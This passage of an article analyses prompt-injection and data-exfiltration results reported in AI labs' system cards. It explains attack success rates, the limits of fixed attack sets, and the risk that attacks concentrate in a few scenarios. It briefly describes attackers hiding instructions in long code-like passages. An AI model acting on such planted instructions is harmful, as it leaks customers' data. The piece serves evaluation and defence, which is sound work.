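GPT-5.6 Sol appears twice with different results, so readers can't use figures from different cards to rank models. Within the tracker, the gap between Google's models and Nvidia's Nemotron is far too large to be an effect of the method. Anthropic's models were close behind Google's. Kimi and Nemotron are open models, and companies that run them on their own servers have to supply their own safeguards.

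Products often resist attacks better than the models inside them. In Anthropic's browser tests, attacks on Opus 5 succeeded 3.7% of the time without extra safeguards. With the safeguards, no attack succeeded in 129 scenarios, as The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection* also reports. The success rate in other scenarios of the same kind could still be as high as about 2%, based on the rule of dividing 3 by the number of trials without a successful attack.

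OpenAI also measured how often its models disclose data in difficult office tasks with ambiguous instructions and complicated permissions. In one test, the prompt also included a policy on when to ask the user for approval.

| Model | Data exfiltration without the policy | With the policy |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 14.1% | 8.8% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 4.3% | 4.5% |

The written policy helped the older model considerably but made no clear difference to the newer one. OpenAI designed the tasks to cause mistakes, so the rates should be lower in everyday work. But every task had a safe solution, and one of the strongest models available in September still disclosed data in more than 4% of cases.

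### What an average over fixed attacks hides

An attack success rate of 2% over 28 scenarios could mean that the attack works 2% of the time in each scenario, or 56% of the time in one and never in the other 27. If that one scenario is answering customers' emails, the mail-order company would be badly exposed despite the model's excellent score.

The results for Opus 5 suggest that some scenarios are riskier than others. A single attempt succeeded 0.2% of the time. If every scenario were equally risky, at least one of 15 independent attempts would succeed about 3% of the time, but the reported figure is 2.0%. Repeated attempts add less when the successes are concentrated in a few scenarios.

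Average results from different kinds of test can also conflict. Anthropic highlighted Mythos 5's record result on Gray Swan's benchmark, but the model's scores on coding and computer-use safety fell between those of two earlier models. Simula's *CAISS analysis of Anthropics system card for Fable 5 and Mythos 5* objects that the card reports weaker blocking of injections "quietly beneath a reassuring headline". Both the record result and the weaker blocking can be accurately reported, and a company should look for the test closest to its own use.

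A fixed set of attacks is also older than the models tested on it. For its card, OpenAI tested GPT-6 Astra with attacks from contests held in early 2026, before the model existed, so nobody had adapted them to its weaknesses. Zico Kolter, a founder of Gray Swan, warns that attackers now use long passages resembling code, which models mistake for genuine instructions. The checksum page in the Framing Gap worked similarly.

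An attack success rate counts every leak equally, whether the attacker gets a single order number or the whole customer list. The company should therefore record how many customers' details got out in each failed test. A model that fails in 2% of attacks may do less damage if its order lookup returns only one customer's record per session than a model that fails in 0.2% but has access to the entire database.
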